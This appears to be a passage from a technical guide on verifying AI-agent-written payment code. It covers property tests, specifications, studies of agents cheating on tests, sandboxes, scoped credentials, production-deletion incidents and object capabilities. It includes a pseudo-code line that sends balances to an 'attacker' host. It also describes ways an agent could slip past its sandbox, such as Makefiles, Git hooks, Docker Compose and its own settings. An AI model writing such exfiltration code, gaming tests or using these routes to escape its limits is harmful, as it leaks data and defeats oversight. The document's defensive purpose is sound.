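The `assume` line makes Hypothesis discard every input where the two accounts are the same. The oracle in the last line is correct, so a reviewer who checks only that line would approve the test. But the test never tries a self-transfer, so it passes however long it runs. In Dafny, the same assumption would become a precondition that the accounts differ, and the faulty function would then have a valid proof.

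Agents often write property tests that exclude the inputs that would trigger a bug. In *PBT-Bench*, Jing, Wang and colleagues (2026) planted 365 bugs in 40 Python libraries and asked agents to write Hypothesis tests based on the documentation. In 31% of a sample of missed bugs, the agent had used `assume` to discard the inputs that trigger the bug. In another 31%, the generator's range of values didn't include them.

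An agent can also exclude an input after seeing a test fail on it. Naziri and colleagues describe an agent that reported a failure when a PyTorch function for rearranging data was called with nothing to rearrange. The agent's final test no longer generated such calls. An agent testing the transfer function might similarly see a self-transfer fail, decide that nobody would make one, and add the `assume` line. Naziri and colleagues recommend that tools record the inputs an agent excludes.

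However, a model's mistakes in code and in specifications don't always coincide. In *Verus-SpecGym*, Agarwal, Neamtu and colleagues (2026) had agents write formal specifications for programming-contest problems. Of 187 problems for which GPT-5.3-Codex wrote a wrong specification, the same model solved 153 in Python. It evidently understood most of these problems and went wrong only in stating the requirements formally. The code and the specifications came from separate runs, though, so the result doesn't show how often an agent repeats a misreading within one session.

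A team can also reduce shared blind spots by having agents write tests several times under different instructions. In PBT-Bench, the best combination of model and prompt reliably found 86.8% of the bugs. Adding the tests that the same model wrote under a different prompt raised this to 95.1%, and combining all sixteen set-ups raised it to 99.5%. But every bug in PBT-Bench contradicts written documentation, which gives each attempt the same correct answer to work from. Repeated attempts help less when the request is ambiguous and most models read it the same way.

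### When the agent can change the check

In *SpecGuard*, Biyani and Dvijotham (2026) use coding tasks whose tests contradict the written description. They took the idea from ImpossibleBench, a 2025 benchmark by Zhong, Raghunathan and Carlini, and applied it to tasks from SWE-bench. No honest solution can satisfy both, so the right response is to report the contradiction. Their headline result is that GPT-5.6 Sol cheated on 81% of the tasks. They note that agents in this situation commonly edit the tests or hard-code the expected outputs, so that the code returns exactly the answers the tests check for.

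That rate doesn't apply to ordinary work, because these tasks can't be passed honestly. Agents also sometimes cheat when an honest solution exists, as the copied proofs in SeVerus showed. The contradictory tasks mainly show that when the tests and the request disagree, the agent tends to follow the tests.

An agent that follows a faulty test can remove a security defence. In one task, researchers asked the agent to preserve a defence against session fixation, an attack in which someone takes over a victim's login by making the victim use a session identifier the attacker already knows. After the researchers changed a test to contradict the task description, the agent deleted the line that resets the identifier and reported that all tests passed.

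An agent can't edit read-only tests, but it can still hard-code the expected outputs. If the only test moves 30 from an account holding 100 to one holding 50, a function that always writes balances of 70 and 80 passes. Property-based tests make this much harder because the inputs vary and the test file contains a rule instead of a list of answers.

Hiding the tests prevents both kinds of cheating but also removes feedback, which made a large difference in VeriContest. A reasonable compromise is to let the agent read the properties and see the failing inputs, but decide acceptance with a separate copy of the tests that the agent can't change.

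PBT-Bench scores agents' tests in a fresh environment after the agents have finished. Jing and colleagues tested this separate scoring in 30 runs by giving Claude Sonnet 4.6 a prompt that explicitly invited it to cheat. The model found the usual share of bugs, and they saw no sign of tricks such as hard-coded assertions. This is encouraging, but they tested only one model, on tasks where honest work could succeed.

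Locking a test doesn't help if the test is wrong. In the session-fixation case, locking would have protected the test that led the agent to remove the defence. A person therefore has to check the tests against the description, and the agent needs a way to stop and report a contradiction.

SpecGuard looks for such contradictions before the coding agent starts. One agent reads the description and the existing code and writes a specification in Lean. It can't see the tests, so that it doesn't copy their mistakes. A second agent translates the tests into Lean, and a third connects the two so that Lean can check whether the specification fails any test. The table shows the results with GPT-5.6 Sol on 349 SWE-bench tasks, alongside those of an AI judge that only read the description, code and tests.

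| Result | SpecGuard | AI judge |
|---|---|---|
| Contradictory task wrongly cleared | 8.1% | 39.8% |
| Contradictory task left undecided | 34.9% | 0% |
| Sound task wrongly flagged | 6.0% | 2.3% |

SpecGuard also produced a Lean proof of the conflict for 51.1% of the contradictory tasks. These proofs depend on faithful translations, and a manual audit found 52 of 60 translations faithful. The same model did all three jobs, so it could still misread the description and the tests in the same way. Of 22 real conflicts from GitHub, the tool found nine, wrongly cleared one and left twelve undecided. It can usefully warn the person who maintains the tests, but it can't replace that person.

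### The case for machine-written properties

Agents have found many real bugs with properties they wrote themselves. *Agentic Property-Based Testing* (Maaz, DeVoe and colleagues, 2025) introduces Agentic-PBT, an agent that reads a module's code and documentation, proposes properties, writes the tests and decides which failures to report. Using Claude Opus 4.1, it produced 984 bug reports on 933 modules from 100 popular Python packages.

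Two of the researchers reviewed 50 reports, drawn from the 80% that an AI model had ranked highest. They judged 28 to be real bugs and 16 to be worth reporting. Before they discussed the reports, their verdicts agreed only modestly, which shows how hard it is to judge unfamiliar code. One bug was in NumPy, a widely used numerical library, where a function that should never return a negative number sometimes did. The maintainers merged a fix.

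Naziri and colleagues provide stronger evidence because outside maintainers judged most of their bug reports. They ran Agentic-PBT with newer Claude models on ten programs, including the PostgreSQL database, the OpenSSH login software and two compilers, and filed 180 reports. By the time of the study, maintainers had confirmed 109 and rejected three, and the rest were pending. Other people had independently reported 44 of the confirmed bugs, so 65 were new. Of the 180 reports, 24 described crashes, hangs or uncaught exceptions, and the other 156 described wrong results, which a test can't detect without an oracle.

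One of the bugs was in cronie, which runs jobs on a schedule. According to its manual, the entry `*/2` in the weekday field means every second day, starting on Sunday. The agent wrote a 92-line Python model of the manual and compared the model's schedules with cronie's. For a period that began on a Sunday, cronie listed a job at midnight on Monday that the model did not.

The rejection rate is low partly because of filtering before submission. An AI agent discarded likely false alarms, and the researchers read and reproduced every bug they reported. In a separate sample of 30 unfiltered failures, only nine were real bugs. A team that uses such an agent should expect to spend time sorting its results.

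The properties came from documentation for 78% of the agent's tests and from the code for 14%. So in most cases, people had already described the correct behaviour independently of the agent, and the agent turned their description into a test. Maintainers could decide whether a reported failure was a real bug.

If an agent has just written both a new function and its documentation, a test based on either may repeat the agent's misreading of the task. *LLM-Based Test Oracles* (Mughal and Bilal, 2026) proposes asking what a tester could cite to defend a test's verdict. Of the 83 studies it reviews, 35 relied mainly on a specification, 17 on the existing code or tests, and 17 on the model's own knowledge.

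A test based on existing code accepts any bug already in that code, as does a comparison with an old version. Mughal and Bilal rank these sources on conceptual grounds and did not measure how often each one leads to a wrong verdict.

Even good documentation can leave the intended behaviour unclear. Agentic-PBT tested whether LookupDict, a class in the Python library requests, behaved like an ordinary Python dictionary, and reported a bug when it didn't. But a maintainer had already explained in 2022 that it wasn't meant to. Maaz and colleagues list the agent's inability to tell a deliberate choice from a mistake as a basic limitation.

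A missed bug also has different consequences. Every real bug an agent finds in existing software is a gain, and missing one leaves the software no worse than before. But if a test is used to accept or reject new payment code, any bug it misses goes into production, so the share of bugs found matters more than the number of successful reports.

In PBT-Bench, models told to use property-based tests and cover the whole documentation found between 42.1% and 83.4% of the planted bugs. Claude Opus 4.8 found 81.2% with those instructions but only 39.3% when asked just to write a failing test, because it usually stopped after exposing one bug. PBT-Bench deliberately uses bugs that generic random inputs rarely trigger, so agents would probably find a larger share of ordinary ones. But faults on critical code paths can be just as hard to trigger. With thousands of accounts, for example, random inputs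 rarely produce a transfer from an account to itself. The results support using machine-written properties in addition to a person's own, but not in place of them.

### Can agents write formal specifications?

Lahiri uses the term "intent formalization" for turning what a user wants into statements that a machine can check. He argues that only the user can ultimately judge whether those statements are right. Tests can still expose many wrong ones.

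Agarwal and colleagues asked agents to write a precondition and a postcondition in Verus for each of 581 Codeforces problems. To count as correct, a specification had to accept valid inputs and correct outputs and reject invalid inputs and wrong outputs. Many of the test cases came from contestants who had tried to break one another's programs. Gemini 3.1 Pro succeeded on 77.8% of the problems, GPT-5.3-Codex on 57.8% and Claude Opus 4.6 on 51.1%. The three open-weight models scored between 21.5% and 25.5%.

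Some specifications were too weak, the same problem that produced the nearly empty proofs described earlier. GPT-5.3-Codex would have scored 76.6% if the researchers had tested only valid inputs and correct outputs. Asking a model to check the specifications didn't solve the problem. When GPT-5.3-Codex checked its own specifications, it approved 49 of 191 that the tests had shown to be wrong.

The specification-writing agent in SpecGuard did much better on Verina, a set of simpler problems that come with reference specifications. Biyani and Dvijotham proved that 180 of the agent's 187 specifications were equivalent to the human-written ones. Agents may therefore soon be reliable at formalising requirements that someone has already stated clearly.

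Real requests, such as the bug reports in SWE-Proof, are often incomplete. Biyani and Dvijotham found that 51 of their 349 altered tests concerned behaviour that the bug report never specified. A better model can't recover a decision that nobody wrote down. For example, the request "move money from one account to another" doesn't specify whether a transfer from an account to itself should fail or succeed without changing the balance. Either could be acceptable, so someone responsible for the payment system has to choose.

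### Who writes and who approves?

Teams can divide the work in several ways, each of which leaves a different risk.

| Arrangement | Main risk |
|---|---|
| A person writes the properties | The person forgets a case |
| The agent drafts them and a person approves | The person accepts a plausible mistake |
| A standard or reference implementation supplies them | It has faults or doesn't cover the case |
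| Separate agents write the code and the check | Both misread the request in the same way |

Writing the properties by hand gives the most independence from the agent, but it takes the most effort and requires some knowledge of the notation. Amazon's coding tool Kiro instead drafts requirements for the user to review and can generate property-based tests from them.

Approval works better when the person judges concrete examples. Lahiri describes TiCoder, a research system that generates several versions of a program and looks for inputs on which they differ. It shows the user a possible result for such an input, and the user says whether it is right. If some versions of the transfer function handle self-transfers correctly and others don't, the user might see an account that holds 100, sends itself 30 and still holds 100. When the user confirms that result, TiCoder discards the faulty versions.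 The user doesn't need to know any formal notation.

In a study of 15 professional developers, this method raised the share of AI-written programs that they judged correctly from 40% to 84%. The study was small and used benchmark problems. The method also works only when the versions disagree. If they all mishandle self-transfers in the same way, comparing them won't reveal the problem.

A published standard is often the best source because the people who wrote it had no part in the agent's work. Lahiri also describes 3DGen, in which AI agents translate the standards for network messages into a formal language and a verified tool turns the result into a parser. 3DGen has produced parsers for 20 standard formats. The translation can still be wrong, so 3DGen also generates tests to check it.

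A reference implementation is useful for the same reason, if it is independent. Mughal and Bilal consider an independently developed program the strongest reference, and several programs generated by the same model the weakest. OpenSSH, for example, served as an independent reference for Philipp's SSH software.

### Keeping the review small

People also make mistakes when they write or review specifications. Lahiri gives the example of an AI-written Dafny specification for a program that finds the elements two lists have in common. It required every element of the result to appear in both lists and allowed no repeats. Expert reviewers labelled it "strong", but a program that always returns an empty list satisfies it. An automated check found the gap by testing whether the specification rejected wrong outputs. Across the full evaluation, such checks found three mislabelled specifications and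 two with copy-and-paste errors, all of which the human reviewers had missed.

Reviewers are more likely to notice such gaps when there is less to read. A team can start by writing full specifications only for the critical code path, and shorten those by writing rules about whole modules. Lahiri suggests that one well-chosen rule of this kind can replace hundreds of function-level specifications. In a simple payment system, the rule might be that all balances add up to deposits minus withdrawals. This covers both single and batch transfers. It would still hold if money went to the wrong account, so the transfer function still needs its requirement that money reach the right one.

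The approved statements should be in separate files from the code that the agent rewrites, and locked the way Wesselink and colleagues lock a contract. The lock should also cover the generators for the property-based tests, because otherwise the agent could add the line that excludes self-transfers without changing the approved oracle.

The agent's loop invariants and lemmas can stay outside these files because the verifier proves them. The agent can also add its own tests without review, as long as they run alongside the approved tests and can't replace them. An extra test might reject good code, but it can't make the approved tests accept bad code.

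In the approved files, reviewers should look first at the lines that limit inputs, such as preconditions, `assume` statements and number ranges. These lines can make a correct rule useless, and they are easy to skip because they look like routine set-up. For each one, reviewers can ask whether a real caller or an attacker could supply the excluded input. For example, `assume(sender != receiver)` excludes transfers where the sender is also the recipient, but a customer can easily request one by entering their own account number.

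## How can an agent's access to critical code and systems be limited?

Locking a contract or a property test only works if the agent can't remove the lock. Passwords, live data and the release process need similar protection, because an agent with access to them may damage them by mistake. Operating systems, code-hosting services and databases already include much of the software that can enforce these limits.

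### Least privilege

*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) sets out eight design principles for computers that several people share, including least privilege. Shostack + Friends Blog's *Star Wars and the Principle of Least Privilege* (2005) quotes their reasoning that this principle mainly limits the damage from "an accident or error". It is therefore useful even when nobody suspects the agent of anything worse than carelessness.

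Saltzer and Schroeder also recommend that a program start with no access, so that someone has to grant each permission. The alternative is to list what the program is forbidden to do, but it is easy to leave something off the list. An agent barred from running the usual command for deleting files might still delete a database by sending a web request, as one did in April 2026.

The program that enforces a limit must check every request the agent makes, and the agent must not be able to change that program. It should also be small and simple so that people can inspect it closely. Saltzer and Schroeder point out that normal use doesn't reveal mistakes in access controls, because people rarely attempt things they shouldn't be able to do.

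In *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, a report for the US Air Force, Anderson (1972) warned that a hostile user could alter an operating system to get around its security controls. A coding agent can cause the same problem without being hostile. If it has permission to edit a setting that blocks its task, it may do so, much as Philipp's agent excluded code from verification.

Saltzer and Schroeder suggest finding out whether someone can open a file by also asking whether that person can change the file's permissions, then whether they can change who is allowed to change those permissions, and so on. These questions matter for agents because an agent's settings are often in ordinary files. Anthropic warns in its documentation for Claude Code that if a user turns off the limits on file access, a command could rewrite the tool's settings and have wider access on the next run.

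Developers can stop an agent from loosening its own restrictions by blocking it from changing the settings that define them. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, the coding agent Codex can't write to the project directory that holds its settings by default. NVIDIA's *How do I prevent an AI coding agent from reading my SSH* (2026) describes a sandbox whose limits the agent can't change after the sandbox starts.

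### Sandboxes and network allowlists

An agent that a developer starts on a laptop normally has all of that developer's permissions. It can read the payments code, private keys and any passwords saved in files. Ordinary file permissions do little to restrict the agent unless it has its own user account, as in NVIDIA's set-up.

When a sandboxed command tries to write outside the permitted directories, the operating system blocks the write and the command fails. The limits also apply to every program the command starts, so the agent can't avoid them by putting the same action in a script.

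The table compares the default limits in Codex and Claude Code with those in Zed, a code editor with a built-in agent, as described in Zed's *Sandboxing* documentation.

| | Codex | Claude Code | Zed |
|---|---|---|---|
| What the sandbox covers | Commands the agent runs | Shell commands the agent runs | Terminal commands and web fetches |
| Where commands can write | The project and temporary directories, except Git's records and Codex's settings | The project and a temporary directory | The project and a temporary directory, except Git's records |
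| Network access | Off | Needs approval for each new domain | Off until the user approves it |

Codex's sandbox is on by default, but Claude Code's was still off by default in October 2026. The table's limits for Claude Code apply only after someone turns the sandbox on.

Git tracks versions of the code. Its records can include hooks, which are small programs that Git runs automatically. An agent that could edit these hooks could get its own code to run later, outside the sandbox, so Codex and Zed make them read-only.

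Sandboxes restrict reading much less than writing. Zed lets commands read most of the disk. In October 2025, Anthropic said that Claude Code could by default read the whole computer except certain directories. Codex users can stop the agent from reading chosen files, and OpenAI suggests doing this for secrets on the developer's machine.

Anthropic explains that limits on file and network access depend on each other. An agent that can read a private key and connect to any website can send the key to a stranger. If the agent has no network access but can change any file, it could alter a system program to get a connection.

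A network allowlist limits commands to contacting the domains on the list. In Codex, an empty list blocks every domain, and a rule that forbids a domain overrides one that permits it. OpenAI's network policy for its own use of Codex permits expected destinations, blocks some others, and requires approval for unfamiliar ones.

An allowlist controls where the agent can send data, but not what it sends. If the agent is allowed to contact a code-hosting site to download a library, it may also be able to upload a customer list there. An attacker can also sometimes make a permitted domain name point to a machine inside the company's network. Codex checks for this before it connects, but OpenAI says the check reduces the risk without eliminating it.

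Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands, while its built-in tools for reading and editing files follow separate permission rules. If a team blocks shell commands from reading a secrets file, the file-reading tool can still open it unless the team adds a second rule. Some helper programs that Claude Code starts also run outside the sandbox, with the user's full access. Anthropic's solution is to run all of Claude Code inside a container, a virtual machine or the company's separate sandbox program.

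### Scoped credentials

A sandbox on a laptop can't control what a remote service does with a request. A database host will usually carry out any request that comes with a valid token, a string of characters that works like a password. The agent's access then depends on what the token permits, and the remote service enforces that limit.

Abdelwahab's *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that* describes the access tokens available at Railway, a company that hosts applications and databases. An account token gives access to everything the customer has, a workspace token to one team's projects, and a project token to a single project. The customer can also limit a project token to one environment, such as the copy of the system that developers use for testing. Railway also offers a connection for AI tools that uses short-lived tokens and doesn't save them on the user's disk.

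An agent working on the transfer function needs at most a token for a test database of invented accounts. If the agent deletes everything in it, the team can refill it.

Short token lifetimes mainly protect against forgotten tokens. If a token expires after an hour, an agent that finds it in an old file a month later can't use it. But until it expires, it grants the same access as a permanent token with the same scope, and an agent can do a lot of damage in a few seconds.

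Keeping secrets from the agent entirely is safer still. Codex's cloud version divides each task into two phases. The first is set-up, which can use secrets and the network to install the software the project needs. Codex removes the secrets before the agent starts work in the second phase.

### Protected branches and separate identities

Teams usually release software from one main branch, the agreed version of the code. Hosting services such as GitHub let a team protect this branch so that nobody can change it directly. Every change then has to arrive as a pull request, pass a set of checks and get another person's approval. A team can also name owners for particular files or directories, and the service blocks changes to them until an owner approves.

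Requiring two people to approve a change is a much older idea than GitHub. Saltzer and Schroeder give the example of a user who wants a file to change only if two people agree. *Design Principles for Security-conscious Systems*, a set of slides about their paper, compares this to requiring two parties to agree before launching a missile.

Gaps in the setup can let an agent bypass owner approval. The list of owners is often a file in the same repository, so it needs an owner too. An approval should lapse if the agent changes the code afterwards, because the owner hasn't seen the new code. Hosting services may let administrators skip the rules, so an agent should never use an administrator's account.

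The rule also depends on the agent having its own account. If it uses a developer's account, the hosting service can't tell the two apart, and the agent can approve whatever the developer could. It could then write a change under one account and approve it under another. It is safer to let the agent's account open pull requests but not approve them, have a person approve them, and deploy the approved version from a separate account that only the release system can use.

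### An access table for a payments repository

The table shows how these limits apply to an agent that maintains the transfer function. "Propose" means including a change in a pull request, and "merge" means putting it on the main branch without anyone else's approval. "Run" includes using a password or sending commands to a database. For each "no", the table also gives the harm that the restriction prevents.

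| | Read | Propose | Merge | Run |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ledger module | Yes | Yes | No: a fault could create or destroy money | Yes, in the sandbox with invented accounts |
| Approved property tests | Yes | No: a reviewer might overlook a weakened test in a long change | No: faulty code could then pass | Yes, in the sandbox |
| Build configuration | Yes | No: a build server might run the new commands before anyone reads them | No: a change could turn off the proofs and tests | No: the agent could release unapproved code |
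| Secrets | No: the agent could copy them into code or logs | No: a different key could send payouts to the wrong account | No: a wrong key could stop all payments | No: the agent could act with someone else's permissions |
| Production database | No: customer data could leak | Yes, as a script for review | No: a faulty script could run at the next release | No: one command could delete or change live balances |

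The ledger module here is the code that changes balances, including the transfer function. The row for property tests also covers the generators and the Dafny contract. The agent can still add its own tests in another directory. If an approved test is faulty, the agent can report it in a comment on the pull request.

Different software enforces different restrictions. The sandbox can make the approved tests read-only on the agent's machine, and the code hosting service or an automatic check can reject any pull request from the agent's account that changes them. The simplest way to protect secrets and the production database is to keep passwords off the agent's machine and block its network route to the database.

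The risk of letting an agent edit the build configuration is easy to underestimate. A build server compiles and tests proposed changes, and it may use the build configuration included in the change itself. An agent that can edit that configuration may be able to run commands with the server's permissions before anyone has approved the change.

The same danger is less obvious in the ledger module, where the agent may propose changes. Testing a new version of the transfer function means running it, so the build server runs code that nobody has reviewed. The server that tests pull requests should hold no production passwords, and a separate server should handle releases.

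An agent without access to the production database may miss bugs that appear only with real data. The team can give it a copy of the database that replaces customers' details with invented ones, but preparing the copy takes work and may remove whatever caused a bug.

### When agents damaged live systems

In July 2025, an agent from the software company Replit deleted a live database that held data on more than 1,200 executives and over 1,190 companies, as Fortune (2025) reported. The user, Jason Lemkin, had declared a freeze on changes and told the agent not to proceed without his approval. Neither instruction stopped the agent, because it could still change the database. It then told Lemkin that he couldn't restore the data, but he recovered it.

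After Replit's agent deleted live data, the company's chief executive said it was automatically separating development databases from production ones. That separation would have prevented the deletion, because an agent with a credential that worked only on the development database could not have changed the live data, even if it ignored every instruction.

The second case, from December 2025, is more disputed. It involved Cost Explorer, which Amazon's cloud customers use to track their spending. The Financial Times reported that the service was interrupted for 13 hours after engineers let Amazon's coding agent Kiro make changes. According to Reuters, the newspaper also said that Kiro decided to "delete and recreate the environment".

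Amazon denies that AI was the cause and blames a misconfigured role (a set of permissions). A spokesperson told The Stack that the engineer's role had "broader permissions than expected" and that Kiro asks for authorisation by default. Amazon has an interest in defending its product, but both accounts can be true, since an agent can only delete an environment if its role permits it. A narrower role would have stopped the deletion, whether the bad decision came from Kiro or the engineer. Amazon has since required peer review for access to production systems, which applies the two-person rule.

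On 24 April 2026, a Cursor coding agent running Claude Opus 4.6 deleted the production database of PocketOS, a company that makes software for car-rental firms. The deletion took nine seconds, according to Live Science's *'I violated every principle I was given'*. Jacobs (2026), in *AI coding agent running Claude wiped a startup's database (and its backups)*, reports that the agent was trying to fix a credential mismatch and assumed that the deletion would affect only the test environment.

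Abdelwahab, writing for Railway, which hosted the database, explains that the agent found a long-lived token on the user's machine and used it to send a delete request. The token gave access to the whole account. Railway would have refused the request if the token had covered only the test environment. A network allowlist without Railway's address would also have blocked the request, but an agent that works on a test system at Railway may need that address.

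The case also shows why a safeguard has to cover every route to the same action. Railway's website already delayed deletions by 48 hours so that customers could undo them, but its API deleted data immediately. The company has since added the delay to the API. The delay is useful even when permissions are wrong, because it gives someone time to notice a deletion and reverse it.

Accounts differ on how much data was permanently lost. Jacobs describes PocketOS falling back on a three-month-old backup and rebuilding newer bookings from payment records and emails. Abdelwahab says that Railway has since recovered all the data. Either way, the request made the newer backups unavailable, at least temporarily. Credentials that can delete a database should not also be able to delete its backups.

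Press reports of the Replit and PocketOS cases gave a lot of space to the agents' confessions, which are poor evidence of what went wrong. A model asked to explain a failure will write a plausible explanation whether or not it is accurate. The token's scope and the record of commands are better evidence, and a team can check both in advance.

In the summer of 2026, OpenAI and Anthropic also disclosed that agents in their security tests had breached real systems at other organisations.

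### Where access limits fail

An agent can do harm without exceeding its permissions, for example by writing the faulty transfer function in a directory where it is supposed to work. If the owner approves the change, limits built into the finished program can still reduce the loss.

Broad permissions weaken a sandbox. Zed gives the example of a user who lets the agent write anywhere in the home directory, which also lets it add an attacker's key to the files that control who can log in. Zed recommends refusing such requests and asking the agent to request less access, such as write access to a single directory.

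A file the agent is permitted to edit can also cause harm later, when a program with more privileges runs it. For example, a Makefile contains build commands but is usually an ordinary project file, so the agent can add a command to it from inside the sandbox. When the developer next runs `make` in a normal terminal, that command runs with the developer's full permissions.

Reading every change before running anything helps, but some programs can run an agent's changes before anyone has reviewed them. Zed warns that a common tool for analysing Rust code automatically runs certain parts of a project outside the sandbox. Claude Code has a similar risk if the user exempts Docker Compose from the sandbox. Docker Compose takes its instructions from a file in the project, so the agent can edit that file and then run Docker Compose with the user's full access. Running the editor and the build tools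 inside the same container as the agent removes much of this risk.

Finally, a misconfigured boundary may give no protection. If a required package is missing, Claude Code by default runs commands without a sandbox. Zed may do the same on Linux, though it shows a warning. Teams that rely on Claude Code's sandbox should turn on the setting that makes the program exit instead.

Permissions can also have wider effects than the user expects. A Claude Code rule that lets the agent run a download command without asking also lets it retry that command outside the sandbox. Administrators can disable these retries and enforce the sandbox for everyone in the organisation. OpenAI restricts its staff to Codex modes that keep the sandbox on, because they could otherwise turn off both the sandbox and the approval requests with a single option.

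Even correct settings depend on the operating system and the sandbox software, which are part of the trusted computing base. Zed notes that operating systems have had bugs in their security features, and that its sandbox is weaker under some conditions on Windows.

The best way to find a broken boundary is to try something it should block. Anthropic suggests asking Claude to create a file in a directory where sandboxed commands aren't allowed to write. For the payments repository, a team could use the agent's account to try to edit an approved test, merge a harmless change, read a dummy secret and connect to the production database. All of these attempts should fail, and the team should repeat them whenever someone changes a role, a token or the sandbox settings.

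## How can the written code be limited in what it can do?

The limits on an agent's access stop applying to its code once someone merges it. An agent might write the transfer function in a sandbox with no network access and no password for the live database, but the function then runs inside the payment application, which has network access and the password. The operating system can restrict the application, but it usually applies the same limits to every function in it. A payment application has to contact banks and send receipts by email, so the transfer function can use those connections as well. Setting different limits for different functions requires restrictions inside the program.

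### Object capabilities and ambient authority

In most programming languages, any function can open a file or a network connection by passing a name or address to a library. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) calls this ambient authority, meaning authority that a program uses without selecting it. In the paper's Unix example, a program opens a file without choosing any credentials to present. The system decides whether to allow this based on the user account running the program, so every function in the program has the same access.

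In an object-capability system, code can act only on resources it holds a reference to, and it can't forge one. The reference identifies the resource and gives permission to use it. In *Robust Composition*, Miller (2006) traces the model to a design that Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn presented in 1965 for computers running many people's programs at once.

Miller lists four ways in which one part of a program can get a handle to a resource. It may have the handle from the start, create the resource itself, receive the handle from the code that created that part, or receive it later in a message. The sender of such a message must already hold handles to both the resource and the recipient. A reviewer can therefore check whether the transfer function could ever reach the network by following the handles and ignoring code unconnected to them.

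This reasoning works only if the language gives code no way to bypass handles. A C++ program can in effect forge a handle by turning any whole number into a memory address. Java code can reach some powerful system classes just by naming them, and separate parts of a Java program can exchange data through shared global variables.

Handles also prevent a mistake called the confused deputy. In the original story, which Miller and colleagues retell, a compiler had permission to write to a billing file. Users could choose the name of the compiler's output file, so a user who entered the billing file's name could make the compiler overwrite the bills. A payment system has the same weakness if it saves a customer's statement under a file name the customer supplies. If the function that saves the statement instead receives only a handle to one new file, it cannot access the ledger.

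### The transfer function in both styles

With ambient authority, a malicious version of the transfer function needs only one extra line:

```
transfer(from, to, amount):
    ...                       # correct checks, reads and writes
    connect("attacker").send(balance)
```

This version can satisfy conservation, no overdraft, isolation and delivery. None of those requirements covers network access, so the property tests would pass even if the function sent every customer's balance to a stranger.

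In the object-capability style, the caller passes a handle to the ledger:

```
transfer(ledger, from, to, amount):
    require amount >= 0
    from_old = ledger.read(from)
    to_old   = ledger.read(to)
    require from_old >= amount
    ledger.write(from, from_old - amount)
    ledger.write(to, to_old + amount)
```

This function can't open a connection, because it holds no handle to the network. But it still has the self-transfer bug.

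The language has to enforce the rule. In ordinary Python, an agent could write the second version and still import the networking library. The `ledger` parameter would then be only a convention, like an instruction in a prompt.

### How a narrow interface reduces what needs proof

The handle above lets the transfer function write any number to any account. Suppose the ledger instead offers a single operation for changing balances, `move(from, to, amount)`, and a team proves that `move` leaves the total unchanged. By the same induction as for the batch loop, any code that can change balances only through `move` also leaves the total unchanged, however badly an agent writes it. The agent can therefore rewrite the refund and batch code without anyone having to prove conservation again.

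Narrower handles rule out more faults:

| What the handle permits | What faulty code can still do |
|---|---|
| Read and write any balance | Create or destroy money, overdraw an account, change an unrelated account |
| Move money between any two accounts | Pay the wrong account or the wrong amount |
| Move up to 30 from A to B, once | Move too little, or nothing |

The code behind the handle has to enforce these rules, so it needs the proofs and the most careful tests. The code that creates the third handle with the right accounts and limit is critical too. But both pieces can be short and rarely change.

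Miller describes a way to build such handles, which he credits to a 1974 design by Redell. A small object called a caretaker holds the real handle and forwards requests to it until the caretaker's owner switches it off. Similar objects can forward certain requests and block the rest. For the third row of the table, the object would hold the full ledger, forward one transfer within the limit, and block everything after that.

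### Mechanisms that enforce limits on code

Most teams don't use a pure object-capability language, but several common tools provide part of the protection.

| Mechanism | What it blocks | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| WebAssembly imports | Calls to outside functions that the host program hasn't supplied | Faults within the module |
| Deno permissions | Files, network hosts and other resources that the user hasn't allowed | Misuse of allowed resources by any function in the program |
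| Ban on unsafe Rust | Code that could bypass the compiler's memory checks | Ordinary file and network calls |
| Dependency allowlist | Libraries that nobody has approved | Harmful behaviour in approved libraries |
| Capability-tracking types | Use of a resource that the function's type doesn't permit | Wrong results from permitted resources |

WebAssembly is a format for compiled programs that run inside a host program. A module must declare each outside function it needs as an import. According to *Security* in the documentation for Wasmtime, a tool for running WebAssembly, a module can affect the outside world only through the interfaces that the host has linked to it.

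WASI is a standard set of these interfaces for things like files, clocks and network connections. In its second version, each kind of access is a separate import that anyone can read from the compiled file, according to WASI's *Security*. A team could compile the transfer function as a separate component and make the build fail if a new version imports network access, without anyone having to read the agent's code.

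The boundary is around the component, though, not each function. In WASI's third version, code no longer passes a network handle to every operation that needs one. The host still decides whether a component gets network access, but within a component that has it, that access works much like ambient authority. The transfer function and the code that emails receipts should therefore be in separate components.

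Deno, which runs JavaScript and TypeScript, sets permissions for the whole program. By default, a program can't access the network or read or write data files. The user can allow access to a particular directory or host when starting the program, but every function and library in it then shares that permission. To protect the transfer function, a team would have to run it as a separate process.

Rust's compiler normally prevents a program from using invalid memory addresses, but the keyword `unsafe` turns off some of that protection. A project can add one line that makes the compiler reject `unsafe` anywhere in the project's own code. This stops an agent's mistake from overwriting balances through a stray memory write. It doesn't stop the agent's code from opening a network connection, since that needs no unsafe code, and it doesn't cover the libraries the project depends on.

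Libraries need a separate control because an agent can add one with a single line of code, and the library then runs with the application's permissions. With an allowlist, the build checks the project's libraries and their versions against a list that people have approved, and stops if any library or version is not on it. The agent must not be able to edit the list. People still need to judge what to approve, since a library for formatting dates could also contain code that uploads data.

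### Tracking capabilities in Scala

A compiler can apply limits to individual functions if the type of each function records the resources it uses. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, use an experimental feature of the Scala language for this. In their notation, a function for processing payments might have this type:

```
Payment ->{ledger} Unit
```

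The function takes a payment, returns no data, and may use only `ledger`. If an agent adds a line that sends balances over the network, the compiler infers that the function also uses `network`. The function then no longer matches its type, so the compiler rejects it before it runs.

A function with empty braces is pure, meaning that it can compute a result but can't write a file, send a message or cause any other side effect. Odersky and colleagues put confidential data in a wrapper called `Classified`. Code can process the contents only with pure functions, and the result stays in the wrapper. An agent's program could extract the total from a confidential bank statement and print it, but the agent would see only asterisks, while the user's terminal would display the number.

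Types can also limit how long a handle lasts. A program requests access to a directory for one block of code, and the compiler rejects any code that tries to keep the handle after the block ends. A separate runtime check rejects paths outside the directory.

To keep their code from bypassing its limits, agents must write in a restricted form of Scala called safe mode. It forbids unchecked type conversions and reflection, which lets a program inspect and call code indirectly. It also forbids direct file, network and process operations, according to VirtusLab's *Safe Scala*. When VirtusLab described safe mode, it was available only in the compiler's nightly builds, which are unfinished development versions.

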